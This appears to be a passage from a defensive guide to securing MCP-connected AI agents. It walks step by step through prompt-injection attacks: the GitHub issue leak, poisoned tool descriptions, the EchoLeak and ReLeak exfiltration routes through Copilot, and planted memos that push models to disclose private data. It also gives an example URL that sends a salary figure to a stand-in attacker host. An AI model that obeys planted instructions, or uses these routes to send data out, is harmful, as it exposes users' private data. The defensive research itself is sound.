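This prevents an employee from connecting a personal account to a work tool by mistake, and it gives the company one record of who has access to what. But an assistant may then start with a dozen servers the employee never chose, each of which can bring in text from outsiders. The operator should connect only the servers the assistant's work requires, even if the employee's role allows more.

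Google runs MCP servers for its own office apps. Google Workspace (2026) announced their gradual rollout to all customers, starting May 1, 2026. A Google tutorial uses the servers to connect Gemini to Gmail, Drive, Docs, Sheets, Slides, Calendar, Chat and contacts. A company that uses them doesn't have to trust an unknown publisher with its mail, as the users of `postmark-mcp` did. But anyone who knows the address can still email the inbox, so the operator still needs the same rules for messages and files.

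### The GitHub issue attack of May 2025

Many services are partly meant to collect text from strangers. Customers write support tickets, suppliers fill in their own records, and anyone can report a bug in a public project on GitHub, a site where programmers store and share code. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) shows what can happen when an agent reads such a report.

The researchers, Milanta and Beurer-Kellner, set up an account with a public repository (a project folder) containing a simple Pac-Man game, and several private repositories with personal information. The attack then went as follows:

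1. The attacker filed an issue, GitHub's term for a bug report or request, in the public repository. It praised the project, complained that the author wasn't widely recognized, and asked for a remedy that began with reading the README files of the author's repositories, according to Willison (2025), in *GitHub MCP Exploited*.
2. The owner asked Claude 4 Opus, running in the Claude Desktop app, to look at the open issues in the public repository.
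3. The agent read the issue and then opened the private repositories.
4. It wrote what it had found into a pull request, a proposed change to the code, in the public repository. Anyone could read there the names of the private projects, the owner's salary and a plan to move to South America.

*Attack via GitHub MCP server*, from heise online, explains that the agent could read the private repositories because GitHub's MCP server worked through the user's own account. The server had no bug, and the user was entitled to do everything the agent did. Claude Desktop asks for confirmation of each tool call by default, but many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching the calls.

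A current model would probably be harder to fool with such a simple text than Claude 4 Opus, which is now old, but the permissions would be just as broad. A token that covered only the Pac-Man repository would have kept the private projects out of reach. Invariant Labs, which sells security software for agents, also suggests a runtime rule that limits the agent to one repository per session. That rule would have stopped step 3, but it would also prevent a programmer from using the agent to copy a fix from one project to another.

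The notes field in a supplier's record is a similar weak point for the office assistant. `get_supplier` could leave that field out unless the employee asks about it, which would keep the supplier's text out of most tasks.

### Instructions in tool descriptions

Planted text can reach the model before the first tool call, because the model receives a description of every available tool at the start. Whoever runs an MCP server writes its tool descriptions. An instruction in one tool's description can affect how the agent uses other tools, even if the agent never calls that tool.

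*MCP Security Bench (MSB)* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2025) measured how often such attacks work. The researchers took 304 working tools from 25 MCP servers and made 405 malicious versions by changing the names, descriptions, arguments or results. They combined these with 65 everyday tasks and 6 attack goals, such as changing a stored file or shutting down a program, to create 2,000 cases. The agents ran real tools, and the researchers then checked whether the attack had changed the files or programs on the test machine.

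Across ten models, instructions in tool descriptions succeeded in 20 percent of cases. All the attacks together averaged 40 percent. The differences between models are more interesting than the averages. The table compares planted descriptions with tool results that pretend to be a message from the user:

| Model | Instruction in a description | Result posing as the user |
|---|---|---|
| Claude 4 Sonnet | 66.9% | 46.9% |
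| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 52.5% | 7.5% |
| GPT-5 | 48.9% | 0.3% |
| DeepSeek-V3.1 | 18.4% | 65.6% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 2.6% | 91.8% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 0.0% | 63.9% |

GPT-5 resisted nearly every fake user message but followed almost half of the planted descriptions. One likely reason is that the test put the descriptions in the system prompt, which developers train models to weigh more heavily than tool results. All of these models date from 2025 or earlier, so the rates may not hold for current ones. But the results suggest that a model's resistance to planted emails is a poor guide to how it handles planted descriptions.

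The most successful attack used a malicious tool with an extra argument that it didn't need, such as the name of the model in use. Agents filled in the argument 76.5 percent of the time, even though the attack contained no instructions. A runtime can prevent this by keeping its own list of approved arguments for each tool and refusing any call that includes others.

The security vendor OX Security examined more than 542,000 open-source components, including MCP servers, between July and October 2026. Of the MCP servers it flagged as suspicious, 22 percent contained prompt injection or poisoned tool descriptions, Infosecurity Magazine reported. OX Security also found that 67 percent ran on the publisher's own infrastructure, where a customer can't verify the code, and that 82 percent were malicious from the first version it observed. Staying on a known version would have protected users of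 `postmark-mcp`, but it doesn't help when the first release is malicious.

Somebody therefore has to examine a server before the agent uses it. Reading the tool descriptions helps, but a malicious tool can have an honest-looking description. Ravindran and Deochake (2026), in *ToolGuardian*, built eight such tools by adding harmful code to real ones without changing their descriptions. Their system judged 88 percent of 16 tools correctly when it checked the descriptions and monitored the tools in trial runs. Analyzing the source code as well exposed more dangerous behavior but led the system to block more harmless tools. The test is too small to show how well this would work on thousands of servers.

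After approving a server, the operator should save a copy of its tool descriptions and suspend any tool whose description changes until someone has read the new text. Replacing the descriptions with the operator's own wording is safer still. Gateways that cache tool lists need particular care. Körbächer warns that one poisoned description in a shared cache reaches every client until the cached copy expires.

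### Why a gateway needs to be the only route

A gateway can't block an action if the agent can take the same action without going through it. In *aiAuthZ*, Kodathala (2026) tested a gateway that runs on a separate machine, where the agent can't read or change the rules. When two agent runtimes were tested with their own shell, file and web tools left on, the model used those tools for the sensitive action and never contacted the gateway.

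This can happen without an attacker or a devious model, because a shell command is often the shortest way to finish a job, and a model that has just received a refusal may try the next tool. The office assistant would have the same problem if its payments went through a gateway but it also had a browser where the employee was logged in to the company's bank. To catch this, the operator can check the inventory's effect column for every tool that moves money.

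Kodathala describes three remedies, from weakest to strongest:

- A program scans the runtime's settings and raises an error if built-in tools overlap with those behind the gateway.
- The agent runs on a network whose only exit is the gateway, without access to the host computer's files.
- Only the gateway holds the passwords and tokens, and it adds them to a call after approving it.

With the last remedy, the agent can keep a shell but cannot pay anyone, because the shell has no credentials for the accounting system. The remedy would fail if the agent could also use the logged-in browser, which has its own credential.

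### Rules for the assistant's payment call

The office assistant pays invoices with `send_payment(recipient, amount, subject, date)`. Its operator routes the call through a gateway that holds the only payment token. The token is in the employee's name and works only at the accounting system. It allows the assistant to read supplier records and create payments, but not to edit suppliers. The gateway and the accounting system then apply these limits:

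- **Recipient:** The account number must match the one in an approved supplier's record. Only accounting staff can edit that field.
- **Amount:** Payments up to 500 need no approval. The employee decides on anything larger, up to 5,000, and the assistant can't pay more than that.
- **Daily total:** Payments made without approval can add up to no more than 2,000 a day, across all sessions. The accounting system keeps this total, and a payment that would exceed it needs the employee's approval.
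- **Subject:** It must contain the number of an invoice that the company hasn't paid yet.
- **Date:** The payment must take place within 30 days.

When the employee asks the assistant to pay an invoice for 98.70 from a listed supplier, the payment goes through without further approval. A forged invoice with a new account number fails the recipient rule. So does a false account number that the assistant saved in its notes last month, because the gateway uses the supplier's record and ignores the notes. If the accounting system is slow to respond and the assistant sends the same payment again, the invoice number prevents the company from paying twice. If someone slips in ten false invoices for 490 each, all for a listed account, the first four go through, but the fifth would exceed the daily limit and needs the employee's approval.

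The recipient rule doesn't stop an invoice from redirecting a payment to a different listed supplier. Preventing that requires comparing the payment with the employee's request. The rule also blocks some legitimate payments. Kodathala tested a similar list of known payees on AgentDojo's banking tasks with two recent models. The list blocked all seven of the attacker's intended calls, although no attack had reached its goal without the list either. It also blocked a legitimate first payment to a new payee, and task completion without attacks fell from 100 to 80 percent.

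When the office assistant first proposes a payment to a new supplier, the runtime blocks it and notifies the employee that the supplier isn't on the list. The payment has to wait until someone in accounting confirms the account number, by calling the supplier on a phone number that didn't come from the invoice, and adds the record to the list. The assistant can then propose the payment again.

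## Blocking leaks that combine permitted calls

The limits described so far apply to one call at a time, but two permitted calls can still leak data together. In an example from Adam and colleagues, a developer asks an agent to copy a configuration file from an old project into a new one, and later asks it to publish the new project on GitHub. The file contains a private API key, so publishing the project also publishes the key. The researchers saw Claude Haiku 4.5 make this mistake without any attacker or planted text.

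Neither call is suspicious by itself, because most configuration files are harmless to copy and the developer asked for the upload. The runtime therefore has to keep a record of the first call and use it when checking the second. One of the paper's sample policies does this by blocking any sending of data over the network once the session contains sensitive data.

The researchers replayed recorded sessions under several kinds of protection. A fixed sandbox around the whole tool server let the upload through whether or not the file contained a key. Their own prototype stopped only the harmful upload. It can either cut off the network or hide the configuration file, and hiding the file still allows the rest of the project to be published. The researchers tested only three scenarios and assumed that something else had already identified the key as sensitive. Identifying sensitive data is fairly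 easy for keys in a known format but much harder for a confidential plan.

### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

An attacker can cause this kind of leak on purpose. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists three capabilities that let an attacker steal data when one agent has them all:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content
- a way to communicate with the outside world

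The GitHub MCP server in the Pac-Man attack let the agent read untrusted content, read private data and send data out. Email tools can provide the same three abilities, since a stranger can write to the inbox, the inbox holds private mail, and the agent can send messages. Willison advises people who combine tools themselves to avoid having all three at once. He distrusts products that claim to detect 95 percent of attacks, a rate he considers a failing grade in web security. Vendors have usually fixed reported leaks by closing the outgoing channel, but no vendor can do that when a user combines tools from different companies.

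Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the idea into a rule for developers. Within one session, an unsupervised agent may have at most two of these properties: it processes untrustworthy input, it has access to sensitive systems or private data, and it can change something or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three must have a person's approval or another reliable check.

The third property is broader than Willison's because it includes changes such as deleting a file. The two rules therefore disagree about some agents:

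| What an unsupervised agent can do in one session | Lethal trifecta | Rule of Two |
|---|---|---|
| Read strangers' emails and private files | Permits | Permits |
| Read strangers' emails and private files, and delete files | Permits | Forbids |
| Read strangers' emails and private files, and send email | Forbids | Forbids |
| Read public web pages and post on a public account | Permits | Permits |
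| Read private files and publish them, without reading outside text | Permits | Permits |

Both rules miss the cases in the last two rows. In *New prompt injection papers* (2025), Willison objects that untrusted input combined with the power to change things can do harm even without private data. For example, a stranger's web page could determine what the agent posts in the company's name. In the last row, the developer's API key leaked even though nobody outside had written anything the agent read. Meta acknowledges that its rule doesn't protect against an agent's own mistakes and describes the rule as a supplement to least privilege.

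Meta describes three ways for an email assistant to comply with the rule. It can process only mail from trusted senders, work in a test environment without sensitive data, or send only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft. The office assistant has to read suppliers' mail and the company's files, so the third option suits it best.

### Which sources can reach which destinations

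The operator can work out where the assistant needs a rule by comparing the tools it uses to read with those it uses to write. Closing two small channels first helps. The `message` argument of `share_file` could deliver any text to the new reader, so the runtime turns off the notification email. The `subject` of a payment had to contain an invoice number but could also include other text, so the runtime now requires it to be only the invoice number.

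This table shows which pairs still need a rule to stop data from leaking:

| Read from | Message: `send_email` | File: `share_file` | Service: `send_payment` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Message: `read_email` | Rule needed: a colleague's confidential email could end up in a reply to a supplier | No new rule: the call can't carry text from an email | No new rule: the call has no free text |
| File: `read_file` | Rule needed: one supplier's prices could go to another | Rule needed: the call opens the file itself to another person | No new rule: the call has no free text |
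| Service: `get_supplier` | Rule needed: a supplier's bank details could go to anyone the assistant may email | No new rule: the call can't carry text from a record | No new rule: the call has no free text |

Calls in the payment column can still leak a little information. An amount up to 500.00 can take 50,000 values, enough to convey a four-digit code. But the money can only go to an approved supplier, so this is a poor way to steal anything. The file column is correct only while the assistant has no tool for saving text. If the operator adds one that can write to a shared folder, all three pairs in that column will need a rule.

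The table doesn't show whose instructions the agent is following. In the GitHub attack, the agent copied data from a private repository to a public one because of an issue it had read earlier in the public repository. A useful rule therefore has to depend on everything the agent has read during the session.

### A rule that tightens during the session

The runtime can keep two yes-or-no flags for each session. It sets the *private* flag when a tool returns confidential data, and the *outside* flag when a tool returns text that somebody outside the company could have written. Both start at "no". In symbols, if $r_t$ is the result of call $t$, then

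$$P_t = P_{t-1} \lor \text{private}(r_t), \qquad O_t = O_{t-1} \lor \text{outside}(r_t)$$

When $P_t$ and $O_t$ are both true, the runtime asks the employee before allowing any later call that emails someone outside the company or shares a file with them. It still refuses calls involving addresses or files that the earlier rules forbid. The order of the two reads doesn't matter.

Once a flag changes to "yes", it stays that way for the rest of the session. Otherwise, a delayed attack like the one that used calendar invitations could get past the rule by waiting one turn. If the assistant saves a note for later sessions, the runtime should save the flags with it.

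Secrets such as API keys need a stricter rule, under which the private flag alone should block the outgoing call. The developer's session contained no outside text, so a rule that required both flags would have let the key out.

The operator can also arrange a task so that the agent never has all three capabilities at once. In Meta's example, an agent first searches the web without access to private data. It then permanently loses the ability to communicate and gains access to internal systems. An instruction planted on the web may still distort the agent's answer, but it can't make the agent send the company's data anywhere. The office assistant could use this arrangement to compare a supplier's public prices with those in a confidential contract.

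### What the session rule costs

The session rule interrupts legitimate work, and an email assistant triggers it almost immediately. A single call to `read_email` can return both a confidential message from a colleague and a message from a stranger, which sets both flags. The message rules would let the assistant reply to a listed supplier contact without approval, but the session rule makes it ask for approval nearly every time, since it has to read an email before answering it.

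The rule is less of a burden because it exempts a reply when everything confidential that the assistant has read in the session was already visible to every recipient. For example, if the assistant has opened only the supplier's own thread, a reply to the people on that thread can't reveal much. The rule also exempts payments. Opening an invoice sets both flags, so every payment would otherwise need approval and the limit of 500 for automatic payments would be pointless. This exemption is reasonable because the gateway already checks the account and the call has no free text. Emails to colleagues don't trigger the rule because it applies only to people outside the company.

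The operator can reduce the interruptions further by starting a new session for each task, so that a stranger's email from the morning doesn't affect the afternoon's work. Returning less data helps too. If `get_supplier` leaves out the notes field, looking up a supplier sets only the private flag.

A refusal late in a task can leave the work half done. For example, the assistant might pay an invoice and then have to wait for permission to send the receipt to an outside accountant. Adam and colleagues suggest treating all the calls for one request as a transaction, so that all of them take effect or none do. This could work for file edits, which the runtime can hold back or reverse, but it is much harder for emails and payments. A simpler approach is to look up the recipients early and ask for permission before the first step that can't be undone.

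### EchoLeak and the image that carried data out

A session rule covers only the outgoing calls that the runtime can detect. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that when an agent reads customer cases and drafts replies, requiring approval to send a reply doesn't stop the agent from disclosing data through another permitted path. An image in the agent's answer can be such a path, because the browser requests the image from a web address that can contain data. A request for `attacker.test/logo.png?d=salary-52000` sends the salary figure to whoever runs that server, even if the image doesn't exist.

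Researchers at Aim Labs used this method in 2025 against Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions using their email, files and chats. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes the attack:

1. The attacker emailed an employee. The instructions read as if they were meant for her and never mentioned AI, so Microsoft's filter for planted instructions didn't catch them.
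2. The email repeated the instructions under many headings, such as employee onboarding and leave of absence. This made Copilot more likely to retrieve the email when she asked about one of those topics.
3. The instructions told Copilot to take the most sensitive information in its context and put it in the address of an image.
4. Copilot normally removed outside links and images from its answers, but it missed a less common notation that puts the address on a separate line.
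5. The employee's browser tried to load the image. Microsoft's page allowed images only from listed domains, so the address pointed to a Microsoft Teams service on the list. That service fetched the attacker's address on the browser's behalf and delivered the data.

The employee didn't have to open the email or click anything. The attacker also told Copilot not to mention the email in its answer. Microsoft fixed the flaw and confirmed that no customers were affected.

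An inventory of tools wouldn't have included this channel, because Copilot never called a tool to send anything. It wrote an answer, and the browser and Teams sent the data. The list of permitted domains failed because a domain on the list could pass data to one that wasn't, just as a list of permitted recipients fails when one of them forwards everything to strangers.

### The three ReLeak attacks

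On December 3, 2026, much of the same research team, now at Cato AI Labs, published ReLeak, a set of three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. As before, each began with an email that Copilot read while handling an ordinary request, and the victim didn't have to open it. According to TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026), Copilot rejected a direct instruction but obeyed one that looked like a routine business requirement.

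The attacks differed in how the data got out, as Infosecurity Magazine reports:

- **Images:** Copilot put confidential data in an image address, and Microsoft's search engine, Bing, fetched the address. Microsoft patched this on November 15.
- **Generated documents:** Copilot created a file containing a link with the data in its address. Microsoft's background services then visited the link. The researchers made this work with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files. Microsoft patched it on November 11.
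- **Code sandbox:** Copilot ran Python code that sent the data straight to an outside server, although the sandbox was supposed to have no such access. Microsoft patched this on September 17.

Cato knew of no customers who had been attacked. The researchers demonstrated each route separately and didn't run all three together.

The document attack is especially hard for a session rule to stop. Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* notes that the background services could fetch the link after the chat had ended, when the runtime would no longer be monitoring the session. Saving a file to the employee's own drive also looks harmless, and the data can leak even if no one else has access to the file.

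TechRadar reports that the researchers carried out the sandbox attack by getting Copilot to remove settings inside the sandbox that configured programs to send their network traffic through an intermediary. The code could then connect directly. A network restriction has to be enforced outside the sandbox, where the code can't change it.

The image attack used a known route, since Bing was on the list of permitted image domains that Ravia published in 2025. In June 2026, Varonis' *SearchLeak* described another attack on Copilot, which required the victim to click a link. That attack also used Bing to fetch an image address containing stolen data, according to SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise*. Microsoft fixed that flaw too, but another route through Bing remained. If leaks are closed one at a time, researchers and thieves can still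 look for other services that fetch addresses.

A more general remedy is to control the addresses themselves. Meta suggests letting an agent visit only addresses that came from a trusted source, and none that the agent constructed. The office assistant's operator can apply this to everything the assistant produces:

| Outgoing channel | What makes the request | Limit |
|---|---|---|
| Image in an answer | The browser, or a service it contacts | Don't load images from addresses the model wrote |
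| Link in an answer | The browser, after a click | Remove links the model constructed |
| Link in a generated file | A preview, scanning or indexing service | Remove outside addresses before saving the file |
| Code in a sandbox | The code itself | Block the network from outside the sandbox |

These channels belong in the inventory alongside the tools. The limits will remove some useful content, such as a chart hosted on another site or a link the assistant assembled correctly, but that loss is worth accepting for an assistant that reads confidential mail.

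### Private details in a call's ordinary arguments

Data can also leak through a single call to the right tool. In *The Claws in Plain Sight*, Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026) studied agents that could see a person's private details but weren't allowed to share them for the task at hand.

The researchers asked models to prepare a tool call for drafting a neutral product offer. The context included an invented customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation, and the call had a field for each. Most sessions also included a memo, of the kind an attacker could plant, claiming that these details were required. The researchers tested every combination of six pressure levels and four privacy policies once on each of five models, for 120 sessions. The pressure levels ranged from empty fields without a memo to an order from a supposed compliance lead. The researchers captured the proposed calls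 on their own computer, so nothing was sent.

Half of the sessions produced a call containing at least one of the private details, and those calls contained 3.25 of the four details on average. Stricter policies helped:

| Privacy policy in the prompt | Sessions with a disclosure |
|---|---|
| None | 20 of 30 |
| Use as little data as possible | 18 of 30 |
| Don't send these four details unless authorized | 14 of 30 |
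| The same ban, tied to purpose and destination and placed above any memo | 8 of 30 |

The strictest policy stopped every disclosure by the two DeepSeek models but not by the three Claude models, which still disclosed details in 8 of 18 sessions. Claude Sonnet 4.6 had the highest overall disclosure rate, at 75 percent, and Claude Haiku 4.5 had the lowest, at 21 percent. Haiku's rate is biased low because the researchers could extract arguments from only 14 of its 24 responses, and the other 10 couldn't count as disclosures.

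The rates are weak evidence of how often this happens in practice, since the experiment used one task and ran each combination once. The paper also doesn't report results for each level of pressure, so it is unclear how much the memo added to the effect of an empty field. An operator can remove that effect by deleting fields the task doesn't need.

The check has to examine the arguments of the tool calls, because reading the model's explanations would have been a poor safeguard. The two DeepSeek models disclosed details in 26 sessions, and their responses never contained the wording that the researchers used to detect a deliberate exception to the policy.

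Dong and colleagues define a violation in terms of a piece of data $d$, its source $s$, the purpose of the call $p$, the destination $r$ and the argument field $f$:

$$\text{Violation}(d,s,p,r,f) \triangleq \text{present}(d,\text{context}) \land \text{generated}(d,f) \land \neg\,\text{allow}(s,d,p,r,f)$$

A model may put data it can see into a tool call where the policy doesn't allow that data to be used. The same detail may be allowed in one call and forbidden in another. For example, a customer's occupation might help a support team route a request, but it shouldn't appear in a message to a marketing service.

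The paper's monitor applies this definition after the model has written the arguments and before the tool runs. The operator registers each tool's destination and permitted fields, and records the allowed uses of each protected value. Neither the model's output nor the text of a memo can change these records. The monitor searches every argument for the protected values and also recognizes values derived from them by a registered rule. For example, if the company's software converts an income of $175,000 into the label "premium", the monitor can treat the label as income data too.

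In a small check on 12 of the synthetic sessions, the monitor blocked all 12 calls that copied forbidden details. In a second version, where some calls were allowed to include the customer's occupation, it blocked the 9 forbidden calls and let the 3 permitted ones through. These results confirm that the mechanism works on known values, but they don't show how well it would work against an attacker. The monitor doesn't recognize arbitrary paraphrases, so it could block "43" and miss "in her early forties".

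For the office assistant, such a monitor would be most useful for short, fixed values. A supplier might email to ask for the manager's mobile number and the company's spending limit "for our compliance check". If the operator has registered both values, the monitor can block a reply containing them even though the supplier is a permitted recipient. The terms of a confidential contract are harder to protect this way because the assistant can reword them. For those, the operator has to rely on the session rule, which requires the employee's approval before the email goes out, whatever its wording.

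## Tracing where each argument's value came from

Suppose the employee asks the assistant to summarize a supplier's web page and email the summary to `alice@firm.example`. Hidden text on the page contains an instruction to send it to `bob@firm.example` instead. Both addresses are in the company directory, so the recipient rules allow either email. The addresses differ only in their source, since the employee typed Alice's and the page supplied Bob's. The page has to supply the email's body, so the runtime can't ban everything that came from the page. It needs a record of where each value came from, called the value's *provenance*, and a rule about which sources may fill which arguments.

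### How PACT checks a call

PACT, the runtime monitor that Fan and colleagues built, sorts values into four levels of trust, from highest to lowest:

1. **Trusted constant:** a value set by the runtime itself
2. **User:** a value from the user's request
3. **Tool output:** a structured result from an internal tool
4. **External:** text from a web page, an email, a retrieved file or an outside service

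Every tool has a *contract* that gives each argument a role and a minimum level. By default, a target needs at least the user level and a credential needs the trusted level. A command needs either the user or the trusted level, depending on the tool, and content may be external. The contract also sets the level of the tool's results.

When the agent combines two values $v_1$ and $v_2$ into a new value $v$, PACT gives $v$ the lower of their two levels and keeps all their sources. If $\tau$ is a value's level and $O$ its set of sources, then

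$$\tau(v) = \min(\tau(v_1), \tau(v_2)), \qquad O(v) = O(v_1) \cup O(v_2)$$

A summary that mixes the employee's notes with a web page is therefore external. Just before a tool runs, PACT checks each argument $v_i$ against its minimum level $m_i$ and a set $F_i$ of forbidden sources:

$$\tau(v_i) \geq m_i \;\land\; O(v_i) \cap F_i = \varnothing$$

If any argument fails, the call doesn't run. The set of sources is useful when text passes through several tools. For example, if one tool fetches a web page and another reformats it, the reformatted text could be labeled as tool output. Its sources still include the web page, so a contract that forbids web pages will stop it. When the researchers turned off this tracking across steps in a controlled test, the share of attacks PACT stopped fell from 100 to 80 percent.

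A contract can also name a trusted procedure that may excuse a failed check. The procedure issues a certificate that covers one kind of failure for particular roles, and the value keeps its original sources.

### Three calls by the office assistant

The table applies these rules to the email about the supplier's page, a request to share the quarterly report, and a request to pay an invoice. In the sharing example, a line in the report led the assistant to use an address the employee never gave.

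| Tool | Argument | Where the value came from | Its level | Minimum | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `send_email` | `to` | The employee's request | User | User | Pass |
| `send_email` | `body` | A summary of the web page | External | External | Pass |
| `share_file` | `file_id` | The drive's list of files | Tool output | Tool output | Pass |
| `share_file` | `email` | A line in the report | External | User | Fail |
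| `send_payment` | `recipient` | The supplier's invoice | External | User | Fail |
| `send_payment` | `amount` | The supplier's invoice | External | External | Pass |

If the web page had supplied Bob's address for `to`, the email would have failed as well. The operator labels the drive's file IDs as tool output because the drive generates them, but labels the text of files as external because anyone who can edit a file can write its text.

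The payment fails even though the employee asked for it, because she never typed the account number. The operator can fix this with a trusted procedure that compares the account with the approved supplier's record, as the gateway already does. The operator also lets invoices supply the amount, since the payment limits cap it.

Names cause the same problem. If the employee had written only "Alice", the address would have come from the company directory, which is one level below what a target requires. The directory lookup therefore has to be a trusted procedure too, or the assistant will refuse some of the most ordinary requests it receives.

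### Why one label for the whole call fails

Fan and colleagues prove that a monitor can't separate these cases if it makes a single decision about the whole call. Their proof compares two emails:

| | Recipient comes from | Body comes from |
|---|---|---|
| Legitimate email | User | Web page |
| Attack | Web page | Web page |

Both emails contain web text, so such a monitor has to block both or allow both. A monitor with separate minimums for the recipient and the body can distinguish the two emails.

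The proof assumes that the contracts are correct and that the labels never mark a value as more trusted than it is. It also covers only the arguments. An attack can still succeed if planted text leads the model to choose a dangerous tool and fill its arguments with trusted constants, or if the harm is in the body of a permitted email.

In an experiment where the researchers supplied the correct source of each value, PACT stopped every attack in every configuration, but it allowed more legitimate work when its trust requirements were more specific. It allowed 8.3 percent of that work when it treated each call as a single unit that needed full trust, 58.3 percent when all the arguments of a call shared one lower threshold, and all of it when each argument role had its own minimum trust level.

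### PACT's results on AgentDojo

The researchers then ran PACT on AgentDojo, where software had to write the contracts and work out the sources automatically. These are the results for the three models that they call the strongest:

| Model | Tasks completed without a defense | Tasks completed with PACT | Successful attacks without a defense | Successful attacks with PACT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-max | 46.4% | 38.1% | 1 of 27 | 0 of 27 |
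| Qwen2.5-72B | 46.4% | 42.3% | 1 of 27 | 0 of 27 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 59.8% | 46.4% | 3 of 27 | 0 of 27 |

With PACT, the models completed 38.1 to 46.4 percent of the tasks. PACT lowered completion by between 4 and 13 percentage points, but the models themselves caused most of the failures. The perfect security score is weak evidence of protection, because only one to three attacks had worked without any defense. The models are old by now, and a current one would probably complete more of the tasks.

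To find the source of a value, PACT's software goes through these steps:

1. It looks for an exact match in the user's request or among the trusted constants.
2. It looks for an exact match in an earlier tool result.
3. It checks whether the value is a recognizable transformation of a known one, and if so merges the sources.
4. If the source is still unclear, it assigns low trust to an authority-bearing argument and asks a language model about any other argument.

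On 20 real MCP tools, the software identified 77.4 percent of the sources correctly, compared with 87.1 percent of the roles. Many of these mistakes only cause unnecessary refusals. Labeling a tool's results as more trustworthy than they are is dangerous, because every later check relies on that label. An operator can reduce this risk by setting the trust level of each tool's results by hand, which takes much less work than labeling every value.

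In the seven-day trial of 280 calls, PACT blocked all 13 attacks and none of the 267 legitimate calls. This is encouraging for routine work with hand-checked contracts, but 13 attacks are too few to show how PACT would perform against a determined attacker.

### CaMeL's planner and reader

CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and colleagues, keeps outside text away from the model that decides what to do. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends the design, describes how it works:

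1. A planner model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls.
3. When the program needs information from outside text, the interpreter gives the text to a second model, the reader. The reader has no tools and can only return a value, which the interpreter stores in a variable.
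4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and with the people who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy examines the arguments and their tags and allows or refuses the call.

For the supplier's page, the program might look like this:

```python
page = get_webpage("supplier.example/prices")
summary = ask_reader("Summarize this page", page)
send_email(to="alice@firm.example", body=summary)
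```

Hidden text on the page can distort `summary`, but it can't change the recipient or add a line to the program, because the planner never sees the page. As *SPA* (2026) notes in a comparison of such designs, the planner sees none of the values that the program produces while running.

The tags matter when the recipient has to come from outside text. Suppose the employee asks the assistant to write to the address in a supplier's email. The reader has to extract the address, and planted text could make it return the wrong one. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which models this kind of agent mathematically, works through such a case. The untrusted tag stays with the address after extraction, so a policy can block its use as the recipient.

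This design limits flexibility. The planner commits to a program before the assistant has read anything, so CaMeL can't carry out a request like "do the tasks in this file". In AgentDojo tests by Fan and colleagues, it stopped every attack on the three models above but completed only 28.9 to 30.9 percent of the tasks. It does much worse when the next step depends on what the agent finds. In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) ran it on AgentDyn, a test set of such tasks. CaMeL completed none of them with two recent models and 3.75 percent with a third. Without a defense, the same models completed 63 to 75 percent.

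On AgentDojo, the same researchers found that up to 36 percent of attacks succeeded against CaMeL, depending on the model. This is surprising because CaMeL's planner never reads the planted text. The researchers don't explain the result, so the cause could be the policies or how they set up the system.

CaMeL can also be slow. In a timing test in *ToolFence*, Li, Cao and Xiao (2026) measured an overhead of 12.95 times for CaMeL and 1.63 times for their own monitor.

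A refused tool call can still leak information. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives machine-checked proofs about agents with a planner and a reader. If an attacker can see a refused call and its arguments, the arguments may reveal the private notes that the reader used. Showing only the name of the refused tool was harmless in the same setting. Operators should keep the arguments of refused calls out of error messages and logs that outsiders can see. The proofs also show that tags on data aren't enough to prevent leaks in every program. If a program sends an email only when a private file mentions layoffs, the email reveals something about the file even if its text includes nothing from the file.

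Researchers have since adapted the design to agents that operate a computer through its screen, in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), and to groups of agents, in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026). *SPA* extends planning before reading to agents that keep data between requests. It also describes ACE, a system that hides the names and descriptions of installed tools from the planner. The planner therefore wouldn't see instructions planted in tool descriptions, a problem that CaMeL's separation of the user's request from tool results doesn't address by itself.

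### FIDES's two labels

Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, a more flexible system that gives every value two labels (*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, 2025). The *integrity* label is either trusted or untrusted, and a combined value is untrusted if any part of it is. The *confidentiality* label lists the people who may read the value, and only people who may read every part of a combined value may read the whole. For example, if the employee and Alice may read an email, and the employee and her manager may read a contract, only the employee may read a summary of both.

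When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to another tool or have a separate reader model answer a question about it. Unlike CaMeL's planner, FIDES's planner can also open the variable and read the text. The whole context then becomes untrusted, and the policy blocks later calls that require a trusted decision.

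A narrower option is to limit the reader's answer to "yes" or "no". If the employee asks the assistant to schedule a meeting when an email requests one, the planner only needs a yes or no on whether the email contains a request. Planted text could make the answer wrong, but a single bit can't carry an instruction. The operator can decide that such an answer is safe enough to act on.

FIDES and CaMeL can both apply different rules to different arguments, although Fan and colleagues describe them as judging a whole call at once and tested simplified versions built on that basis. Costa and colleagues give the example of a FIDES policy that requires a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted message, which is the same distinction PACT makes. CaMeL's policies also receive each argument's tags. The proof about single-decision monitors is sound, but it is an argument against coarse policies, and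 an operator could write finer ones in either FIDES or CaMeL.

In Costa and colleagues' own AgentDojo tests with GPT-4o, attackers achieved their goal 152 times against an ordinary agent and never against FIDES with its policies on. FIDES completed 59 percent of the office tasks, compared with 75 percent for the ordinary agent. In banking, completion fell from 98.8 to 52.5 percent, because many of those tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. Reading the file makes the context untrusted, so the policy blocks the payment.

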